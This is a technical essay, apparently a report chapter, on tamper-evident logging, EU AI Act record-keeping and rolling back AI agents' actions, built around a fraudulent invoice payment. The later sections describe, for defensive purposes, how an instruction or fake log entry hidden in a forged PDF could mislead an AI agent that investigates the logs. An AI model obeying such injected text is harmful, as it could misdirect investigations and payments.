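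According to *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions* (Wang, 2026), OpenTelemetry moved its AI conventions to a separate repository in June 2026 and had not officially released them as of 21 August. The international standards bodies ISO and IEC have also been working on a standard for AI system logging, ISO/IEC 24970.

### What European law requires

The European Union's AI Act includes duties to keep records, stop faulty systems and correct them. These duties apply to high-risk systems, which are either put to uses listed in Annex III of the Act, such as screening job applicants, or part of regulated products covered by Annex I. Annex III does not list paying suppliers, so the invoice agent would not normally be high-risk, although ordinary bookkeeping law still applies to its payments.

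Under the Act, a provider is the organisation that develops a system, or has it developed, and puts it on the market. A deployer is an organisation that uses it.

| Article | Who has the duty | Main duty |
|---|---|---|
| 12 | Provider | Build the system so that it can automatically record events |
| 14 | Provider | Design the system so that people can oversee it, override its output and stop it |
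| 19 | Provider | Keep the logs under its control for at least six months |
| 20 | Provider | Correct, withdraw, disable or recall a system that breaks the rules, and inform those affected |
| 26 | Deployer | Monitor the system, suspend it if it may present a risk, and keep the logs under its control for at least six months |
| 73 | Provider | Report serious incidents to the authorities |

The logging duty in the text on the European Commission's *Article 12* page is broad but vague. A system must be able to record events that help identify risks, monitor the system after its release and monitor its operation. Article 12 does not mention prompts, tool calls or delegation. It sets minimum log contents only for certain systems that identify people remotely from features such as their faces. These systems must log the times of each use, the database searched, the input that led to a match and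 the people who verified the result.

Sharif presents his format as a way to meet these requirements, but parts of his legal summary are wrong. He places the six-month minimum in Article 12, although it is in Articles 19 and 26. He also says Article 12(2) requires logs to conform to recognised standards, but the adopted text does not. A company can't assume that using the format makes it compliant.

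Six months may also be too short. If an agent saves a wrong account number in March for a supplier that next bills in October, a company that keeps its logs for exactly six months will already have deleted the entry that shows where the number came from. For data that stays in an agent's memory, it would be safer to keep the record of its origin for as long as the agent can use the data, and for some time afterwards. Subject to data protection law, the Act permits this, because six months is only a minimum and the period must suit the system's purpose.

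Article 14 requires providers to include a stop button or a similar procedure that halts the system in a safe state. According to the European Commission's *Article 26* page, deployers must assign oversight to people with the necessary competence, training and authority. Deployers who have reason to think that the system presents a risk even when used according to its instructions must suspend its use and inform the provider and the authorities without undue delay.

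After a serious incident, the provider must report as soon as it establishes that the system caused or probably caused the incident. artificialintelligenceact.eu's *Article 73* allows at most 15 days in general, ten days after a death, and two days after a widespread infringement or certain other serious incidents. A provider that lacks information can send an incomplete report first. A deployer that can't reach the provider must report instead. Freshfields' *EU AI Act unpacked* says a provider counts as unreachable if it doesn't answer within 24 hours.

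These limits run from the day the provider or deployer becomes aware of the incident, so they do not shorten the delay in detecting it.

Article 73 also requires the provider to investigate and take corrective action, but until it has told the authorities, it may not alter the system in a way that could affect a later evaluation of the causes. Switching an agent off leaves its prompt and policy unchanged, but rewriting the prompt may destroy evidence, so the provider should save a copy of the faulty version before repairing anything.

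Most of these duties do not apply yet. The Digital Omnibus on AI, an amending law, postponed them from 2 August 2026 to 2 December 2027 for systems under Annex III. Systems under Annex I have until 2 August 2028. The law entered into force on 27 July 2026, according to White & Case's *EU AI Omnibus enters into force, amending the AI Act*. One stated reason for the delay was that the technical standards and the bodies that will assess the systems were not ready, according to *Digital Omnibus on AI*, an independent guide to the changes.

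It is less clear whether Article 73, the duty to report incidents, is postponed. The law firm Cuatrecasas' *Digital Omnibus on AI has been published* describes the postponement as covering sections 1 to 3 of Chapter III, which contain Articles 12, 14, 19, 20 and 26 but not Article 73. Accordingly, artificialintelligenceact.eu still gives 2 August 2026 as the date for the duty to report. However, the postponed section 1 contains the rules that determine which systems are high-risk, so a provider could argue that until December 2027 there are no high-risk systems whose incidents it has to report.

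### Personal data and secrets in the logs

A full trail of the invoice agent's work contains suppliers' bank details, employees' emails, confidential contracts and perhaps a password that someone left in a file. Anyone who breaks into the log store gets all of it. Under Article 2(7) of the AI Act, reproduced in Osborne Clarke's *AI Act Redline Digital Omnibus on AI* (2026), EU data protection law still applies to personal data that companies process in connection with the Act.

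One remedy is redaction, which removes sensitive details before the harness writes the entry. AWS, which sells a filter for this purpose, calls this the only reliable time to do it, because every later use of the log raises data protection questions. But redaction may remove the detail an investigator needs. If the filter replaces every account number with "[removed]", nobody can see that the agent paid the wrong account or restore the number later.

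Replacing account numbers with consistent pseudonyms loses less information than removing them. The harness can replace each account number with a code, always using the same code for the same account, and keep the key elsewhere. An investigator can then see that the supplier list contained account A-17 and the agent paid A-52, without seeing either number. The police or the bank will need the real number, so someone must be able to look it up.

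The company can instead keep the full content and restrict who may read it. Kuehlewind and Birkholz suggest that, when a record must include the output of a tool call, software should be able to encrypt it so that only a particular auditor can read it. This preserves the evidence, but an investigator may have to wait for permission while the thief moves the stolen money again. Storing the content separately from the traces can also leave gaps. If the company keeps its traces for a year but deletes the content after 30 days, the older traces will refer to files that no longer exist.

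Access to the log also creates a risk when the investigator is another AI agent. If an attacker hid an instruction in a PDF, a log that preserves the PDF also preserves the instruction, and an agent that reads the log to find the cause of the incident may obey it. The agent that analyses the logs should therefore not be able to make payments or send messages.

A third option is to store hashes instead of content. Sharif requires this and directs anyone who needs the original data to a separate, protected store. Because the same file always produces the same hash, an investigator can confirm that a PDF found in the mailbox is exactly the one the agent read. If the email is gone, the investigator can't learn what it contained from the hash. A copy that a program has re-saved with a new date inside will also fail to match, even if every word is the same.

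Hashes protect privacy less well than they seem to, because people can guess short or predictable texts, hash them and check for a match. Sharif's example of a payment record accidentally shows this with two placeholder hashes that anyone can quickly identify. One, supposedly of the parameters for a sanctions check, begins with e3b0c44298fc1c14, as does the hash of an empty text. The other, supposedly of the agent's reasoning, begins like the hash of the single character "1".

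A bank account number is harder to guess, but a computer can still find it from the hash. If a thief knows the bank and everything else in the payment call, only the ten digits of a German account number are missing, which gives 10 billion possibilities. A computer that tries 10 million a second can test them all in less than 17 minutes. The company can prevent this by mixing a secret key into the text before hashing it. The investigator then needs the key to check a match, so if the company loses the key, the hashes are worthless as evidence.

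Keeping an audit trail can also conflict with the General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), the EU's main data protection law, which gives people a right to have their data erased in some circumstances. In Sharif's format, the company would replace the deleted record with a shell containing its identifier and time, the type of action and the reason for the deletion. An investigator could still see that the agent had called a tool at 09:14, but not which tool or what the result was. The GDPR makes exceptions for legal obligations and legal claims, so a fraudster can't simply have the evidence erased. However, the company can rely on those exceptions only if it knows that it needs the record, and it can't distinguish that record from any other while the wrong payment remains concealed.

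Some details in the trail need more protection than others. The payee, the amount and the account number are already in the company's accounts and at its bank, so hiding them in the trail adds little privacy and makes an investigator's work much harder. The full text of the emails and contracts that the agent read is more sensitive and less often needed, so the company should encrypt it, restrict access to it more tightly and delete it sooner, but still keep it well beyond the time a supplier usually takes to complain.

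## Making records that cannot be altered unnoticed

An audit trail is useful as evidence only if nobody has rewritten it. Whoever diverted the €18,400 could edit one field of the payment record so that the account number seems to have come from the clerk instead of the PDF, and the company might then dismiss an innocent clerk.

Nobody can change a tamper-proof record. A tamper-evident record can be changed or deleted, but a later check will reveal it. Cryptography can make records tamper-evident, but not tamper-proof. Schneier and Kelsey, in *Cryptographic Support for Secure Logs on Untrusted Machines*, point out that no cryptographic method can stop someone from deleting log entries. Preventing deletion takes hardware that cannot erase, such as a write-once disk or a printer.

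An intruder may want to remove the traces of a break-in, and Ma and Tsudik note in *A New Approach to Secure Logging* that an experienced attacker often targets the logging system first. The agent itself could damage the log if it can write to the log's folder, perhaps accidentally while clearing old files to free disk space. The company that runs the agent may also have a motive to alter the log, for instance if a supplier sues and the log shows that a manager had switched off a check. The company is the hardest of the three to guard against because it controls the machines, the passwords and usually the signing keys.

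### The hash chain

With a modern hash function such as SHA-256, nobody has a practical way to find two texts that produce the same hash, which is 32 bytes long. In a hash chain, each record's hash also covers the hash before it:

$$h_i = H(h_{i-1} \,\|\, \mathrm{record}_i)$$

The symbol ‖ means joining the two texts end to end, and $h_0$ is a fixed starting value. Each hash therefore depends on every record up to that point.

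Suppose a log contains four payments, and a thief changes the account number in the second. For each record $i$, an auditor calculates $H(h_{i-1} \| \mathrm{record}_i)$ from the stored values and compares the result with the stored $h_i$. The auditor also has a copy of the original $h_4$ from outside the log.

| What the thief rewrites | Check 1 | Check 2 | Check 3 | Check 4 | Stored h₄ against the outside copy |
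|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Record 2 | Passes | Fails | Passes | Passes | Same |
| Record 2 and h₂ | Passes | Passes | Fails | Passes | Same |
| Record 2, h₂ and h₃ | Passes | Passes | Passes | Fails | Same |
| Record 2, h₂, h₃ and h₄ | Passes | Passes | Passes | Passes | Different |

Each repair breaks the next check, so the thief continues to the end of the log, after which all four checks pass. Anyone who holds the whole log can do this, because a hash function uses no secret. *Agent Flight Recorder* (Bindschaedler, Botha and Siebenbrunner, 2026) describes a prototype that takes about 48 microseconds to write an entry. At that speed, a thief could rebuild a chain of a million entries in under a minute.

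If the thief rewrites the whole chain, the company can detect it only by checking against the outside copy. The chain is still useful, because the company has to protect one 32-byte value instead of a million records.

### Putting the last hash out of reach

Signing the last hash can protect it. Making a digital signature requires a private key, but anyone with the matching public key can check it. A thief without the private key can rebuild the chain but can't sign the new final hash. Signing fails if the key is on the machine the thief has broken into, or if the company itself rewrites the log. Seyedkazemi Ardebili (2026) acknowledges in *NovaFabric* that someone who holds a signing key for his recording system can sign a false record that no later check will detect.

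An outside timestamping service prevents a dishonest key holder from backdating records. It signs the record's hash together with the current time, so the company can't write a record in October and pass it off as one from March.

The company can also give the hash to an outsider. If it emails the latest hash to its auditor every evening, the auditor can detect any later change to what was written before then. Such a hash is called a checkpoint. It is easy to send and reveals practically nothing about the payments. Schneier and Kelsey suggest that several logging machines record each other's hashes in their logs, so that an intruder would have to alter all the logs to avoid detection.

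Bindschaedler and colleagues publish their checkpoints on a public blockchain, a shared ledger that no single organisation controls. With one checkpoint per 100 entries, they estimate that 100,000 entries would cost $6,885 on Ethereum and $2.30 on a cheaper network built on top of it. If the invoice agent writes 2,000 entries in an eight-hour day, the daily cost is about $138 on Ethereum or 5 cents on the cheaper network. A thief could still alter entries made since the last checkpoint unnoticed, which covers up to 24 minutes of the agent's work. The researchers measured the computation on a test network but assumed the prices, which fluctuate.

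The paper argues that a blockchain is worth using when the two sides of a dispute never agreed on who would hold the checkpoints, but that a hash chain on write-once storage is enough for a company's internal audits. It does not test its system against signed or timestamped logs, so a company that already has an outside auditor has little reason to prefer the blockchain.

### Keys that change after every entry

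An intruder who takes over the logging machine may find its current key and use it to rewrite entries made since the last checkpoint. Schneier and Kelsey (1999), in *Secure Audit Logs to Support Computer Forensics*, describe a cheap way to protect those entries. In outline, it works like this:

1. Before the log begins, the logging machine and a trusted machine elsewhere share a secret key, $A_0$.
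2. For entry *j*, the logging machine extends the hash chain to a new value, $Y_j$. It then uses the current key to calculate $Z_j = \mathrm{MAC}_{A_j}(Y_j)$, a message authentication code that only someone with that key can produce.
3. It calculates the next key, $A_{j+1} = H(A_j)$, and permanently erases $A_j$.

An intruder who takes over the machine after entry 500 and finds $A_{501}$ can forge entry 501 and everything after it. But to alter entry 417 and give it a valid code, the intruder would need $A_{417}$, and nobody can run the hash function backwards to get it from $A_{501}$. The trusted machine still has $A_0$, so it can apply the hash function 417 times to get $A_{417}$ and check the entry.

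The trusted machine has to check the code on every entry. Ma and Tsudik show that if an auditor asks it to check only the last code, an intruder can alter entry 417, rebuild the chain from there and pass the check. The intruder has the key for the last entry, so its code is valid.

Nothing protects entries written after the break-in, since the intruder then controls what the machine writes. Schneier and Kelsey add that the problem does not arise if the machine can send each entry to the trusted machine immediately over a reliable connection. An ordinary company server can usually do this, so sending entries immediately is the simpler choice for the invoice agent. Evolving keys are mainly useful for devices that spend time offline and for entries that pile up during a network failure.

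### Merkle trees and transparency logs

A hash chain is a slow way to check a single payment. To connect record 2 with the final hash of a million-record log, an auditor needs nearly all the other records. A Merkle tree solves this by combining hashes in pairs:

```
           root
         /      \
       p          q
      / \        / \
     a   b      c   d
     |   |      |   |
    r1  r2     r3  r4
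```

Here *a* is the hash of record 1, *p* is the hash of *a* and *b* together, and the root is the hash of *p* and *q* together. To prove that record 2 is in the log, the company gives the auditor the record and two hashes, *a* and *q*. The auditor hashes the record to get *b*, hashes *a* and *b* together to get *p*, and hashes *p* and *q* together to get a root. If it matches the root in the checkpoint, record 2 was in the log when the company made that checkpoint. In this procedure, called an inclusion proof, the auditor doesn't see the other three payments.

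Each time the log doubles in size, the proof needs one more hash. A million records need about 20 hashes, or 640 bytes.

A consistency proof shows that a log has only grown. Suppose the log had four records on Monday, when the auditor saved the root, and has eight on Tuesday. The company supplies one hash, *s*, that covers records 5 to 8. If hashing Monday's root together with *s* gives Tuesday's root, the first four records are unchanged. Most proofs need more than one hash, because the old records rarely fill exactly half of the tree, but a proof for a log of a million records never needs more than 21.

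*Certificate Transparency Version 2.0* (Laurie, Messeri and Stradling) describes both kinds of proof for public logs of the certificates that websites use to prove their identity. A website's owner can search these logs for certificates issued in the site's name and notice one that the owner never requested, though the logs can't prevent an authority from issuing a false certificate. *Right to History* (2026) proposes similar logs for the actions of AI agents, and cites an earlier design in which a log of 80 million events required only 3 KB of proof.

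These proofs are useful only if somebody checks them. If an auditor compares checkpoints once a year, an alteration can go unnoticed for a year. The auditor can instead run a program that compares checkpoints every time a new one arrives.

### The measured cost

Bindschaedler and colleagues added the layers one at a time and measured each version on simulated agent activity. They also tested attacks that edited or deleted entries at ten positions in a log of 10,000 entries, and attacks that presented a second version of the log as the original.

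| Version | Typical time per entry (microseconds) | Bytes per entry | Edits and deletions detected | Second versions detected |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plain log | 20.3 | 272 | 0% | 0% |
| Structured entries | 6.0 | 476 | 0% | 0% |
| With a hash chain | 48.2 | 477 | 90% | 0% |
| With Merkle trees | 48.8 | 512 | 100% | 0% |
| With published checkpoints | 47.6 | 512 | 100% | 100% |

Recording entries adds negligible delay for an agent whose model takes seconds to respond. About one entry in a hundred takes 30 milliseconds because the system also signs a checkpoint, which it could do in the background. A replay of 38 actions by real programming agents showed a similar pattern.

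The detection rates are less informative, because the simulated attacker did not recompute the later hashes after changing an entry. The chain missed only changes to the last entry, because no later entry contains its hash. If the attacker had recomputed the hashes, the chain would have missed every change, as it did with the thief in the four-payment example.

Few companies keep tamper-evident records of their AI agents' runs. Seyedkazemi Ardebili read the documentation of eleven tracing tools in June 2026 and found none that made its stored traces tamper-evident. Amazon offers integrity checks for its cloud activity logs, but these do not cover the prompts and responses of an agent's run.

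### What a valid log can still conceal

If the agent pays in a way that bypasses the recorder, the log can omit the payment and still pass every check, because no entry was altered. Bindschaedler and colleagues explicitly exclude completeness from their system's guarantees. In ten test scenarios, NovaFabric captured every model call and tool call it was expected to, but on average only 65.2% of the kinds of evidence the scenarios had declared, because it does not yet record some categories of event.

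Sequence numbers reveal entries that go missing after the recorder has numbered them. If the log goes from 416 to 418, someone can look for 417. But sequence numbers do not reveal a payment that never reached the recorder, so the company also needs an outside count of payments, such as the bank's.

A recorder can also lose entries when its storage is full or unreachable. NovaFabric then drops or summarises events under a stated policy, so that recording never stops the agent from working. That is sensible for an agent that summarises web pages, but for payments it is better to hold each one until the log confirms its entry. A one-hour log failure would delay about 25 of the invoice agent's payments, which is acceptable because no payment would go out unrecorded.

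An entry can also be false from the start. If Horizon had used a hash chain, it would have preserved every false shortfall, and the Post Office might have trusted its figures even more. The remedy is evidence from another party, such as a signed receipt from the bank listing the payee, amount and account number as it received them. The recorder can store this receipt with its own entry. Comparing the two would expose a wrong account number in the entry, but if they agree, it would not reveal that the account belongs to a thief.

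An intruder may also delete the end of the log, which contains the traces of the break-in. Schneier and Kelsey expected the trusted machine to notice missing entries at its next contact. Ma and Tsudik object that it can't, unless it knows how many entries there should be. Suppose the intruder has $A_{501}$ and deletes entries 491 to 500. Forging a new entry 491 would require the erased key $A_{491}$, so the log has to stop at 490. If the log records only unusual events, long periods without entries are normal, so nobody investigates when it stops.

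Regular entries called heartbeats make gaps in a log noticeable. If the machine writes one every minute and the trusted machine receives a log that ends half an hour ago, something is wrong. Ma and Tsudik, who were partly concerned with small devices such as medical implants, consider logging at a fixed rate wasteful. On a company server, however, one 512-byte entry a minute adds only about 0.7 MB a day. Ma and Tsudik instead combine each new signature into a single running signature and erase the separate ones. If anyone removes an entry, the running signature no longer verifies, and the intruder can't calculate its earlier values.

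In a revised draft of his log format, published in August 2026 and valid until February 2027, Sharif recommends ending each session with a closing record that includes a hash of the session and preferably a count of its entries. If that record is missing, a monitoring program should add one that marks the session as a crash. A log that an intruder has cut short would then look like one from a crashed agent, so someone should investigate sessions marked as crashes before accepting that explanation.

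Finally, a company could keep two logs, one showing that the clerk approved the payment and the other that a manager did. It could give the first to the police and the second to its insurer, and each log would pass every check when checked alone. This is called a split view. Laurie and colleagues admit that a dishonest log operator can defeat their auditing mechanisms this way, and say users must therefore treat each log as a trusted third party.

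Readers can detect a split view by comparing checkpoints. If the police and the insurer hold different signed roots for the same number of records, the company has signed two versions of the log. In NovaFabric's design, independent witnesses sign each checkpoint, so the company would also need to deceive or recruit the witnesses. Kuehlewind and Birkholz suggest registering important records with several logs and checking that the logs agree.

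### Why the tool gateway should write the log

The agent's tool calls pass through a program called the gateway, which may already include the reference monitor. The gateway can log the calls it actually receives, while an agent that writes its own log can omit a call or describe it wrongly. The agent should not have the signing key or permission to change the log. The agent's explanations can still be useful, but the gateway should record them as the agent's claims, separate from the record of its actions.

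The machine where records are saved matters, as well as the program that saves them. NovaFabric first saves unsigned records on the machine where the agent runs, and another program collects and signs them later. Before they are signed, an intruder or an agent with access to the files could change them. A gateway on a separate machine avoids this.

Sharif's revised draft recommends an independent recorder that signs with its own key, but only for agents whose identity an authority has verified. Agents with weaker identification may write their own records, so, oddly, the agents about which least is known can have the least reliable logs. The revision also requires high-risk systems to make a record before and after every payment. If only the first record exists, an investigator knows that the agent was allowed to try the payment but not whether the money moved.

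Sharif argues that an independent recorder has no incentive to omit or alter anything. This is true of an outside firm, but the people who control a company-run gateway may have such an incentive, so the company still needs receipts and checkpoints held by outsiders. The gateway also records only what passes through it, so the bank should accept the agent's payments only from the gateway. Bindschaedler and colleagues propose, as future work, running the gateway on hardware that can prove to an outsider which program is running. This would make it harder for the company to use a modified gateway that skips entries.

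### Erasing personal data

A hash chain makes lawful deletion awkward, because removing a supplier's details changes the record and breaks the next check. In Sharif's format, the shell that replaces a deleted record keeps the original hash so that checking programs can accept the break. But a thief could replace an incriminating record with a shell marked as a data protection request. The company should therefore also require a new signed entry identifying who ordered the deletion, and compare that entry with the request.

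Keeping personal data out of the chain is safer. Bindschaedler and colleagues put only hashes and basic details in the chain and store the full content elsewhere in encrypted form. Destroying the decryption key makes the content unreadable without changing any hash. However, their design derives the keys for a whole batch of entries from one key. To erase a single entry, the company has to re-encrypt the rest of the batch under a new key and then destroy the old one.

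### Malicious text inside the log

An instruction hidden in the forged PDF can still mislead an AI system that reads the log during an investigation, and tamper-evident logging can increase this risk. The signature on the entry proves that the gateway recorded the PDF, but a model told that the log is verified may also trust the PDF's contents.

Like the data injections of Choi and colleagues, the PDF could imitate a genuine log entry instead of containing an instruction. For example, it could show the clerk confirming the new account by phone. Choi and colleagues did not test audit logs, so their success rates may not apply to an AI investigator.

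Sharif's measures against log injection include signatures, hashes and checks on the order of timestamps. They help detect a false record added to the log, but not false text inside a genuine record. His format reduces the risk of false text by storing hashes instead of most content. It still requires a readable message for each error, and an attacker who controls a website or tool may be able to choose the text of that message.

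A program should verify the chain first and then give the investigating model only fields with a fixed form, such as times, tool names, account numbers and policy decisions. This also makes searches more accurate. When Bindschaedler and colleagues looked for one policy decision in a simulated incident, a text search returned 79 matches, only one of them correct, while a search of the structured fields returned only the correct one. They designed both the incident and the queries, so the difference may not be as large in real incidents. But an attacker can add false matches to a text search by putting the search terms in a PDF, and can't do this to a field that only the gateway fills in.

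If the investigation requires the PDF's text, a quarantined model without tools can read it and return a restricted answer, as in FIDES. The investigating model should also cite a record number for every finding. If it reports that the clerk confirmed the account in record r-0419, a program can look up that number in the verified chain, and the lookup will fail if r-0419 appears only in the attacker's PDF.

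## Undoing what an agent has done

A sound log can show how €18,400 reached the wrong account, but the company still has to deal with the error in up to four ways. Stopping the agent prevents further wrong payments. Rollback restores the state before the error, for example by putting the old account number back in the supplier list. Compensation is a later action that offsets an effect that can't be undone, such as a refund. Repairing the cause, for example by deleting a false note from the agent's memory, keeps the error from happening again.

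Stopping the agent, refunding the payment and correcting the false note are separate steps. Stopping the agent does not return money it has already sent. If the payment is refunded but the note stays in place, the payment for the next invoice will go to the same thief.

Stopping the agent is the quickest, but stopping it at the wrong time creates a new problem. If someone halts the agent after it has ordered a payment but before it has recorded the invoice as paid, the clerk who takes over may pay the invoice again. To stop safely, as the AI Act requires of high-risk systems, an agent should therefore finish or cancel its current step and leave a list of unfinished work.

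### Resetting the agent and changing the world back

*Revisable by Design* (Zhai, Li and Wang, 2026) divides an agent's state into two layers. The internal layer is the agent's context and the information it has gathered, which software can always reset by cutting the context back to an earlier point. The other layer is whatever the agent has changed outside itself, and only some of those changes can be undone. The harness could remove every trace of the forged invoice from the context in less than a second, but the money would still be gone and the agent would no longer have any record of sending it.

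Zhai and colleagues sort actions by their effect on the outside world. Some change nothing, such as reading a file. Some can be undone exactly, as when an agent deletes a file it created. Others can only be compensated for, such as buying a ticket that can be cancelled for a fee. The rest are irreversible, and the paper's examples include a settled financial transaction. The paper proves that once an agent has taken a compensable action that conflicts with what its user wants, no algorithm can avoid the cost of compensation. The proof follows directly from the definitions, so it reveals little about agents themselves, but the result is useful in practice. A more capable model can't recall a settled payment, but a company can choose a bank whose interface allows cancellation, or arrange the work so that the payment comes last.

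The paper also proposes undoing the earliest action that conflicts with the corrected instructions and everything after it, while keeping all earlier work. In tests with simulated tools, this worked about as well as starting from scratch and discarded 14.6 times fewer completed steps. In those tests, a user had changed the instructions partway through, so the conflict was already known. After a concealed error, someone first has to find out which action went wrong.

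### Reversibility Classes

*Can You Undo It?* (Waghmare and Sufi, November 2026) proposes five Reversibility Classes for the actions of AI agents. Software assigns a class to each tool call before it takes effect, assuming the call will succeed as requested.

| Class | Meaning | Suggested policy |
|---|---|---|
| R0 | The call changes nothing outside the agent | Act freely |
| R1 | The earlier state can be restored exactly | Act, then notify someone |
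| R2 | A known further action leads to an acceptable state at a limited, predictable cost | Ask, or act within a budget approved in advance |
| R3 | Recovery needs a person, an outside process or unlimited effort | Ask every time |
| R4 | The effect cannot be recalled or compensated | Never act without explicit approval |

Exact restoration, the standard for R1, requires that someone saved the earlier state in full, that whoever undoes the change already has the authority to restore that state without another person's help, and that no outsider has seen the change or acted on it.

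Suppose an agent with permission to edit the supplier list replaces a correct account number with a wrong one. If the list keeps old versions and the agent may restore them, the first two conditions hold. An audit log may meet the first, but it does not give anyone the authority to restore the old number. The third condition fails once the bank pays an €18,400 invoice to the wrong account, because restoring the list does not recover the money.

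Under these definitions, the invoice agent's four tools would fall into roughly these classes:

| Tool call | Class | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Read the mailbox | R0 | Nothing changes, provided the tool does not mark or move messages |
| Search company files | R0 | Nothing changes |
| Send an email to a supplier | R4 | An outsider receives the content, and deleting the message does not change that |
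| Pay a regular supplier's listed account | R2 | The company can deduct an overpayment from the next invoice |
| Pay any other account | R4 | A recall depends on the bank, and may fail once the recipient has moved the money |

The payment tool appears twice because its class depends on the account number in the call. A company that trusts its bank's recall procedure might put the last row in R3, but the agent would need approval either way. The email row is more debatable. Zhai and colleagues treat a sent email as compensable because the agent can send a correction. That is reasonable for an email with the wrong payment date, but a correction doesn't help if the agent has sent a supplier a competitor's contract.

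Reading data can also cause harm, because an agent can later send out what it has read. The proposal includes a session guard for this. Once the agent has read data, the guard raises to R4 any call that could send data out, unless every destination is on an approved list.

Defining these classes is easier than assigning tools to them. Waghmare and Sufi labelled 536 existing tools with help from AI. Sufi then rated 148 of them, mostly by approving ratings that an AI system had proposed, and agreed with the original label for 75. Of the 31 tools labelled R1, 30 moved to a higher class. This suggests that people and models easily overestimate how much can be restored, although the review was not independent.

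Whether an action can be undone also depends on the environment. When the researchers closed a browser tab containing an unsaved draft in a plain text box, reopening the tab restored the text in Chromium and Firefox but not in Safari. A company should therefore test a recovery method on its own systems before relying on an R1 label.

### Checkpoints, and the work they can erase

A checkpoint is a saved state to which software can return. *AgentRewind* (Zhuang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) saves one each time the model makes a decision, and each checkpoint includes both the agent's context and the files in its workspace at that moment. If only the files were restored, the context would still include changes that no longer exist, and if only the context were restored, the workspace would contain changes that the context doesn't mention.

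When the agent judges that it is stuck, it chooses an earlier checkpoint and writes a summary of what it has learned. The software restores the context and files from that checkpoint, then adds the summary. On 82 long engineering tasks, agents with this option completed more work than agents that carried on, started again or had a safety model review their actions. These tests did not cover the risk that the summary reintroduces an error. If the agent went wrong because it relied on a forged document, its summary may repeat the false claim after the context is restored.

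Restoring an earlier version can also erase other people's work. Suppose the agent wrongly edits one paragraph of a contract at 10:00, a colleague corrects the delivery terms in another paragraph at 11:00, and at noon someone restores the copy from 9:59. This removes both the agent's mistake and the colleague's correction.

Waghmare and Sufi reproduced this with four versions of a text file. Restoring the whole file erased the later work every time. A three-way merge, which compares the saved original, the agent's version and the current file, removed only the agent's edit when the two changes were in separate paragraphs. When both changes were on the same line, the merge left the file unchanged for a person to resolve. The edits were made one after another, so the tests did not cover a colleague typing during the restoration.

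The same failure can be harder to see in a database. In another test, an agent created a table and someone else later added a row to it. Undoing the agent's action by deleting the table also deleted that row, yet the database then matched its original state exactly. A check that only compared the states before the error and after the repair would have reported a perfect recovery and missed the new error that the repair introduced.

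### A payment sent twice

Restoring a checkpoint can also cause an agent to repeat an action. *ACRFence* (Zheng, Yang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that transfers $500 to Bob and then crashes because a receipt service returns a malformed reply. The software restores a checkpoint from before the transfer. The agent has no record of having paid, so it pays again, and Bob receives $1,000 in total.

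Banks and payment services guard against duplicate payments with an identifier on each request. If a second request arrives with the same identifier, the service treats it as a repeat and does not pay again. This works for an ordinary program, which sends the same request when it retries. A language model writes the request afresh and may give it a new identifier, in which case the bank processes it as a new payment.

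In a test by Zheng and colleagues with a simulated bank, all ten runs restored from a checkpoint made a duplicate payment, while ten runs without a restoration made none. The test shows how the failure happens, but it used one model and placed the checkpoint just before the payment, so it doesn't measure how often the failure happens in practice. Zheng and colleagues also found user reports of repeated or stale tool effects in all 12 agent frameworks they surveyed, including resent emails and repeated charges. A duplicate payment is easy to overlook because each of the two transfers has its own reference and looks legitimate.

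AgentRewind restores the steps before a checkpoint from its log without executing them again, so it does not repeat their effects. But the restored context does not include a payment made after the checkpoint, and only the agent's summary might mention it.

The remedy is to record outside effects somewhere that a restoration does not change, such as the payment gateway. Zheng and colleagues propose that a small language model compare each new call with this record and return the earlier result if the new call means the same thing as a recorded one. They had not yet built this, and the model could make mistakes. For invoices, an ordinary program is usually enough. The gateway can calculate the identifier from the supplier's name and the invoice number, so that two payments for one invoice always carry the same identifier. This would also stop the agent from paying twice when a supplier sends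 the same invoice again, though the company would need an exception for invoices it pays in instalments.

### Transactions and sagas

A database transaction groups changes so that all of them take effect or none do. If the agent has to mark an invoice as paid and reduce the department's budget, a transaction prevents it from doing only one. The program can cancel all the changes with a single command until it commits the transaction.

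After the commit, that command no longer helps. In the tests by Waghmare and Sufi, a database tool committed each update before it returned, so a later rollback command found nothing to cancel. They could still reverse the update if they had saved the old value. For the supplier list, such a reversal might look like this:

```sql
UPDATE suppliers
SET account = 'the saved old number'
WHERE name = 'Paper supplier'
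  AND account = 'the wrong number';
```

The last line prevents the command from overwriting later changes. If a clerk has already entered a third number, the condition matches no row and the command changes nothing. In the tests, this kind of reversal restored the old value unless someone had changed the row since, in which case it left the row alone.

A company can't put its bank inside its own database transaction. For work that spans several systems, Hector Garcia-Molina and Kenneth Salem proposed the saga in 1987. A saga divides a long task into steps, $T_1$ to $T_n$, and pairs each with a compensating action, $C_1$ to $C_n$. If the task fails after step *k*, the software runs the compensating actions in reverse order:

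$$T_1,\; T_2,\; \dots,\; T_k,\; C_k,\; \dots,\; C_2,\; C_1$$

For one invoice, the saga might have three steps:

| Step | Action | Compensating action |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Reserve €18,400 in the budget | Release the reservation |
| 2 | Order the payment | Request a recall or refund |
| 3 | Mark the invoice as paid | Mark it as unpaid |

If step 3 fails, the software requests the money back and releases the reservation only once the money has returned. If it released the reservation earlier, someone could spend the €18,400 again.

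*POLAR* (Kang, Cho and colleagues, 2026) describes two systems that adapt sagas to AI agents. In SagaLLM, a language model writes the compensating actions when it plans the work. STRATUS keeps a stack of completed actions, and a separate undo agent reverses them. In either design, a compensating action can fail. For instance, the payee may refuse a refund, and then a person has to take over.

A more basic weakness of sagas is that they do not detect concealed errors. The software starts compensating when a step reports a failure, but the bank reports a payment to a thief as a success, so the saga completes normally. The compensating actions then run only if somebody discovers the error and starts them by hand.

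Before an agent acts, Kang and colleagues' system, POLAR, searches hand-written rules for a sequence of actions that would reverse the proposed call. It scores each reversing step from 0 to 1 and uses the lowest score for the whole sequence. It refuses the call if that score is below 0.80 or if it finds no sequence.

This prevents a lot of useful work. Across six models and three kinds of customer service, average task scores improved in only 8 of 18 combinations. Four weaker models did better at airline bookings, by 0.11 to 0.18 points, while the strongest models usually did worse. POLAR may have blocked some damaging calls, which task scores don't measure. But refusing every action without a known inverse is clearly too strict for an agent whose job is to make payments.

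### Drafts, delays and the recovery window

Delaying an irreversible step is often easier than trying to undo it. The agent can save emails as drafts and queue payments for the bank to execute later. Until the bank executes a payment, no outsider has received the money, and the company can cancel the payment without asking anyone's permission.

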